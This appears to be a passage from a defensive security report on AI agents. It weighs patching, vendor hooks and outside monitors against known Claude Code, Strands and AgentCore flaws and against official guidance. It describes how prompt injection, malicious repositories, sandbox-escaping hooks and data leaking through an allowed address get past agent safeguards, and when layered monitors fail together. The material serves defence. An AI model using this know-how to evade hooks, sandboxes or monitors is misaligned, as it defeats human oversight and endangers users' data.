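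Claude Code lets users forbid it to read certain files, but these permission rules have needed two fixes for the same weakness. OSV's *GHSA-66m2-gx93-v996* (2025), from October, records that Claude Code could sometimes read a forbidden file anyway, and GitLab's *CVE-2026-25724* (2026) records the same problem in February. Users with automatic updates received the second fix without having to do anything.

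Another flaw, in Claude Code versions 2.1.63 to 2.1.83, let a malicious repository skip the prompt asking whether to trust the folder and run its own hooks immediately, according to the vulnerability tracker Intruder. Anthropic fixed this in version 2.1.84, so a company that relies on Claude Code's hooks also needs to stop older versions from starting.

Canyon Road's *Bugs Happen. Agents Still Run* concludes that companies should patch quickly, expect similar bugs to return, and put further limits underneath the agent. Canyon Road sells such limits. The repeated flaw in Claude Code's file rules supports the paper's argument, but the same reasoning applies to Canyon Road's own product.

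### Covering the time before a patch

Many website operators put a web application firewall in front of their site to inspect each incoming request. When somebody reports a flaw that can't be fixed immediately, the operator can add a rule that blocks requests that would exploit it, and keep the rule until the developers fix the flaw. This is called virtual patching. The flaw is still there, so an attack can succeed if it bypasses the firewall or the rule doesn't recognise it.

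A runtime rule can do the same for an agent. AWS's bulletin on Strands advises customers who can't upgrade yet to keep the shell tool away from any agent that processes untrusted content. It also tells them to run agents that use the tool in an isolated environment with few privileges. A company with its own hook or gateway could turn the first piece of advice into a rule, for example:

```
Temporary rule:  deny the shell tool if this run has read outside content
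Reason:          CVE-2026-18733
Remove when:     every copy runs version 0.8.0 or later
```

Firewall rules can often match the part of a request that triggers the flaw. Injected instructions have no such fixed part, so David C warns against filters that match known bad phrases. A temporary rule for an agent should restrict the action instead. The rule above works however the attacker words the instruction, although it also blocks legitimate shell commands.

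The rule also has to run where the flaw doesn't bypass it. With the AgentCore harness, a rule that ran only after the model proposed a call might never have run, because the attacker could skip the model. Restricting the tools themselves would still have helped. For the Claude Code flaw, the `allowManagedHooksOnly` setting refuses all project hooks, so it should have blocked the malicious repository's hooks. There is no published account of anyone testing this.

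Customers can write a rule for a specific flaw only once they know about it. AWS published the harness flaw after repairing the service, so by the time customers knew about it, they no longer needed a rule. Only a general rule already in place could have protected them before the repair. With Strands, customers still had to install the fix after the flaw became public, and a temporary rule could protect them until they did.

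The company should remove the rule once every copy, including any modified one, runs the fixed version and a harmless test without the rule shows that the approval prompt appears. If the rule stays longer, it keeps blocking legitimate work and can hide a copy that nobody has updated. Setting a review date when adding the rule makes staff less likely to forget it.

The temporary rule that blocks the shell may be worth keeping. Version 0.8.0 restores the approval prompt, but Anthropic's experiment showed that people often approve dangerous commands. If an agent reads text from strangers and rarely needs a shell, blocking the shell is safer than asking a person to approve each command.

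### What two layers miss together

Suppose a vendor hook with a policy misses 5% of attacks and an outside monitor misses 10%. Out of 1,000 attacks, 50 get past the hook. The monitor's benefit depends on how many of those 50 it catches.

```
Both miss  =  missed by the hook × share of those the monitor also misses

Independent failures:  5% × 10%   =  0.5%   (5 attacks in 1,000)
Partly shared:         5% × 50%   =  2.5%   (25 attacks)
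Fully shared:          5% × 100%  =  5%     (50 attacks)
```

If the failures are fully shared, the monitor stops none of the attacks that the hook misses, even though it catches 90% of attacks when tested alone. The share of attacks that get past both can also be lower than 0.5%, and it falls to zero if the monitor catches everything the hook misses.

A company can't tell which case applies from separate miss rates. It has to run both checks on the same attacks and count how many pass both. Such a count is possible for Tether and auto mode's judge because both checked the same recorded sessions in Sistla and colleagues' comparison. Under its default rules, the judge missed 29 of the 344 attacks, and Tether blocked all 29. That is encouraging for this pair, but the test left out attacks that Tether couldn't trace, and some of those might pass both.

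These percentages are also based on the assumption that attacks arrive at random. A real attacker can keep trying until one attack passes both checks, then reuse it against other companies with the same products. David C recommends logging failed tool calls because attackers usually have to refine an attack, and the early failures may reveal it.

A second layer also adds false alarms. If two checks each wrongly block 1% of harmless calls, independently of each other, together they block 1.99%.

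### Why two checks fail on the same attack

Two checks that use the same model are likely to make some of the same mistakes. A planted sentence that misleads one judge will probably mislead another that runs on the same model and reads the same text. Buying the judges from two companies doesn't necessarily prevent this, because both may rent the same model. Fixed rules are a better complement to a judge, since a persuasive sentence can't change them.

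Checks that otherwise have nothing in common can fail in the same way if they share an input. In the Google flaw, an attacker who altered the session history could make it look as if somebody had approved a call. A history rule and a model judge that both read that history would both see the false approval. A check that kept its own log might detect that the approval was false.

When two layers share a computer, a failure in one can damage the other. According to Intruder, before version 2.1.2, malicious code inside Claude Code's sandbox could install hooks that ran outside the sandbox, with the host's privileges, the next time Claude Code started. OSV's *GHSA-ff64-7w26-62rf* (2026) rates the flaw 7.7. The hook settings depended on the sandbox to protect them.

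Shared hardware also means shared outages. Suppose the two checks from the illustration run on one server, the server is unavailable for 1% of calls, and both checks fail open:

```
Server down, neither check runs:       1%
Server up, both checks miss:           99% × 0.5%  =  0.495%
Attacks that get through:              1.495%
```

The outage roughly triples the combined miss rate, although each check works as well as before when it runs. Moving one check to another machine would bring the rate back close to 0.5%.

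Developers can also make the same mistake in separate products. Canyon Road's *A Year of AI Tool Exploits, One Root Cause* recounts how the security company Cymulate found the same faulty file check in Claude Code and Anthropic's Filesystem MCP Server in 2025. The flaw let an agent reach files outside its permitted folder. A company that used one product as a backup for the other would have gained little, because the same attack might have worked on both. Anthropic fixed both in July 2025.

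### Which layer covers which failure

The table compares patching, vendor hooks configured with a policy, and outside checks such as gateways, sandboxes and system monitors. Results marked "documented" come from an advisory, a manual or a test, while those marked "inferred" follow from how the layer works.

| Kind of failure | Patching | Vendor hook with a policy | Outside check |
|---|---|---|---|
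| Code defect | Removes the defect (documented) | Can block dangerous calls until the fix arrives, unless the defect bypasses the hook (inferred) | Isolation limits what an attacker can reach (documented) |
| Injected instruction | Closes known routes, but the model can still follow other instructions (documented) | Can block the resulting call (documented) | Can block the resulting file or network access (documented) |
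| Harmful call within permissions | Has no defect to repair (inferred) | Stops only what its rules or judge recognise (documented) | Can follow the data but usually lacks the user's purpose (documented) |
| Data leaving without a tool call | Closes the route (documented) | Doesn't run (inferred) | Can block the connection if the traffic passes through it (inferred) |
| Check unavailable | Can add a setting that blocks calls (documented) | Usually lets the call continue by default (documented) | Still works if it doesn't rely on the same service (inferred) |
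| Hook not installed | Still fixes known defects (inferred) | Gives no protection (documented) | Still works where the company controls the computer or network (inferred) |

A documented entry can still rest on limited evidence, such as Microsoft's demonstrations of its webhook. The tests of fixed rules provide measured rates, but the researchers attached those rules to their own software rather than to a vendor's hook.

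The entry on data leaving without a tool call applies to CVE-2026-21852, a Claude Code flaw that became public in January 2026. According to Canyon Road, a malicious repository could make Claude Code send the developer's API key to an outside server before asking whether to trust the folder. No tool call took place, so a tool-call hook would not have run. Anthropic fixed the flaw in version 2.0.65.

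Canyon Road says its product AgentSH would have blocked the connection. This is plausible, because a list of permitted addresses applies regardless of the reason for the connection, but Canyon Road reports no test. It also describes a case where such a list would not be enough. In March 2026, the security company Oasis reported that data could leave Claude.ai's sandbox through Anthropic's own address, which the sandbox allowed. To catch this, an outside check would have had to inspect what the agent was sending and whose account would receive it, and customers couldn't add such a check to a sandbox on Anthropic's servers.

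### What official guidance asks for

The most detailed official advice on agents is the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026). Six agencies from five countries wrote it, including CISA and the National Security Agency in the United States and the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC). CISA (2026) announced it on 1 May.

For patching, the agencies ask companies to confirm that outside components come from trusted sources and are up to date. They also ask companies to keep a list of approved tools and versions, verify regularly that these are secure, and be able to return to an earlier working version. The guidance sets no deadline for installing a fix and doesn't discuss temporary rules to use before a fix.

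It calls for a central policy decision on each request at runtime, because a permission checked only at startup can be out of date by the time the agent uses it. A person should approve high-impact actions in advance, and the system's designers or operators, never the agent, should decide which actions count as high-impact. The flaw in Strands broke this last rule because the model could influence whether anyone was asked to approve an action.

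For outside checks, the agencies recommend isolating high-risk agents, preventing agents from changing the logs, and using several independent monitoring systems. They advise against relying on a single security mechanism, but their guidance doesn't address the risk that a central policy service can become a shared point of failure if every hook and gateway depends on it. They also suggest using a second agent to check new tasks against the company's policy, but don't say that this agent should run on a different model.

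The guidance is less clear about what should happen when a check fails. The agencies recommend fail-safe defaults, with agents stopping and referring uncertain cases to a person, but they also recommend that agents keep working partially when some of their functions fail. The first recommendation suggests that a call should not run if its check gives no answer, whereas hooks in Claude Code, Cursor and Copilot Studio usually let the call run by default. The agencies don't mention vendor hooks or how long a webhook should wait, so vendors can interpret the advice as they like.

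The NCSC has also published David C's advice on prompt injection. He passes on a rule from a discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from somebody, its privileges should drop to that person's level. Under this rule, the sales agent could not open the whole lead list after reading a stranger's form entry, because the stranger has no right to see it. The company could follow the rule by giving each enquiry its own run, as with the history rule. David C also advises buyers to distrust any product that claims to "stop" prompt injection, and says a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk may be a poor use for a language model. He doesn't discuss hooks or failed checks either.

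NIST, the US standards agency, is adapting its general security controls to AI systems. It published a concept paper in August 2025 and by early 2026 was collecting comments on an outline for predictive AI, a different kind of system from a tool-using agent. In the meantime, the joint guidance refers companies to NIST's existing work on zero trust, an approach that gives no user or program automatic trust.

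OWASP, a non-profit that publishes lists of common software risks, ranks prompt injection first among risks to language model applications. The joint guidance recommends using OWASP's lists to decide which attacks to plan for. But it warns that the 2025 list for language models may not fully cover attacks specific to agents, and separately refers readers to the 2026 list for agentic applications.

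The agencies' broadest recommendation is that companies should use agents only for low-risk tasks that involve no sensitive data. The Australian Signals Directorate (2026) repeated this on 11 August after an incident involving an agent's unintended behaviour. The sales agent's job would not qualify, because it involves reading customers' contact details and sending email to strangers.
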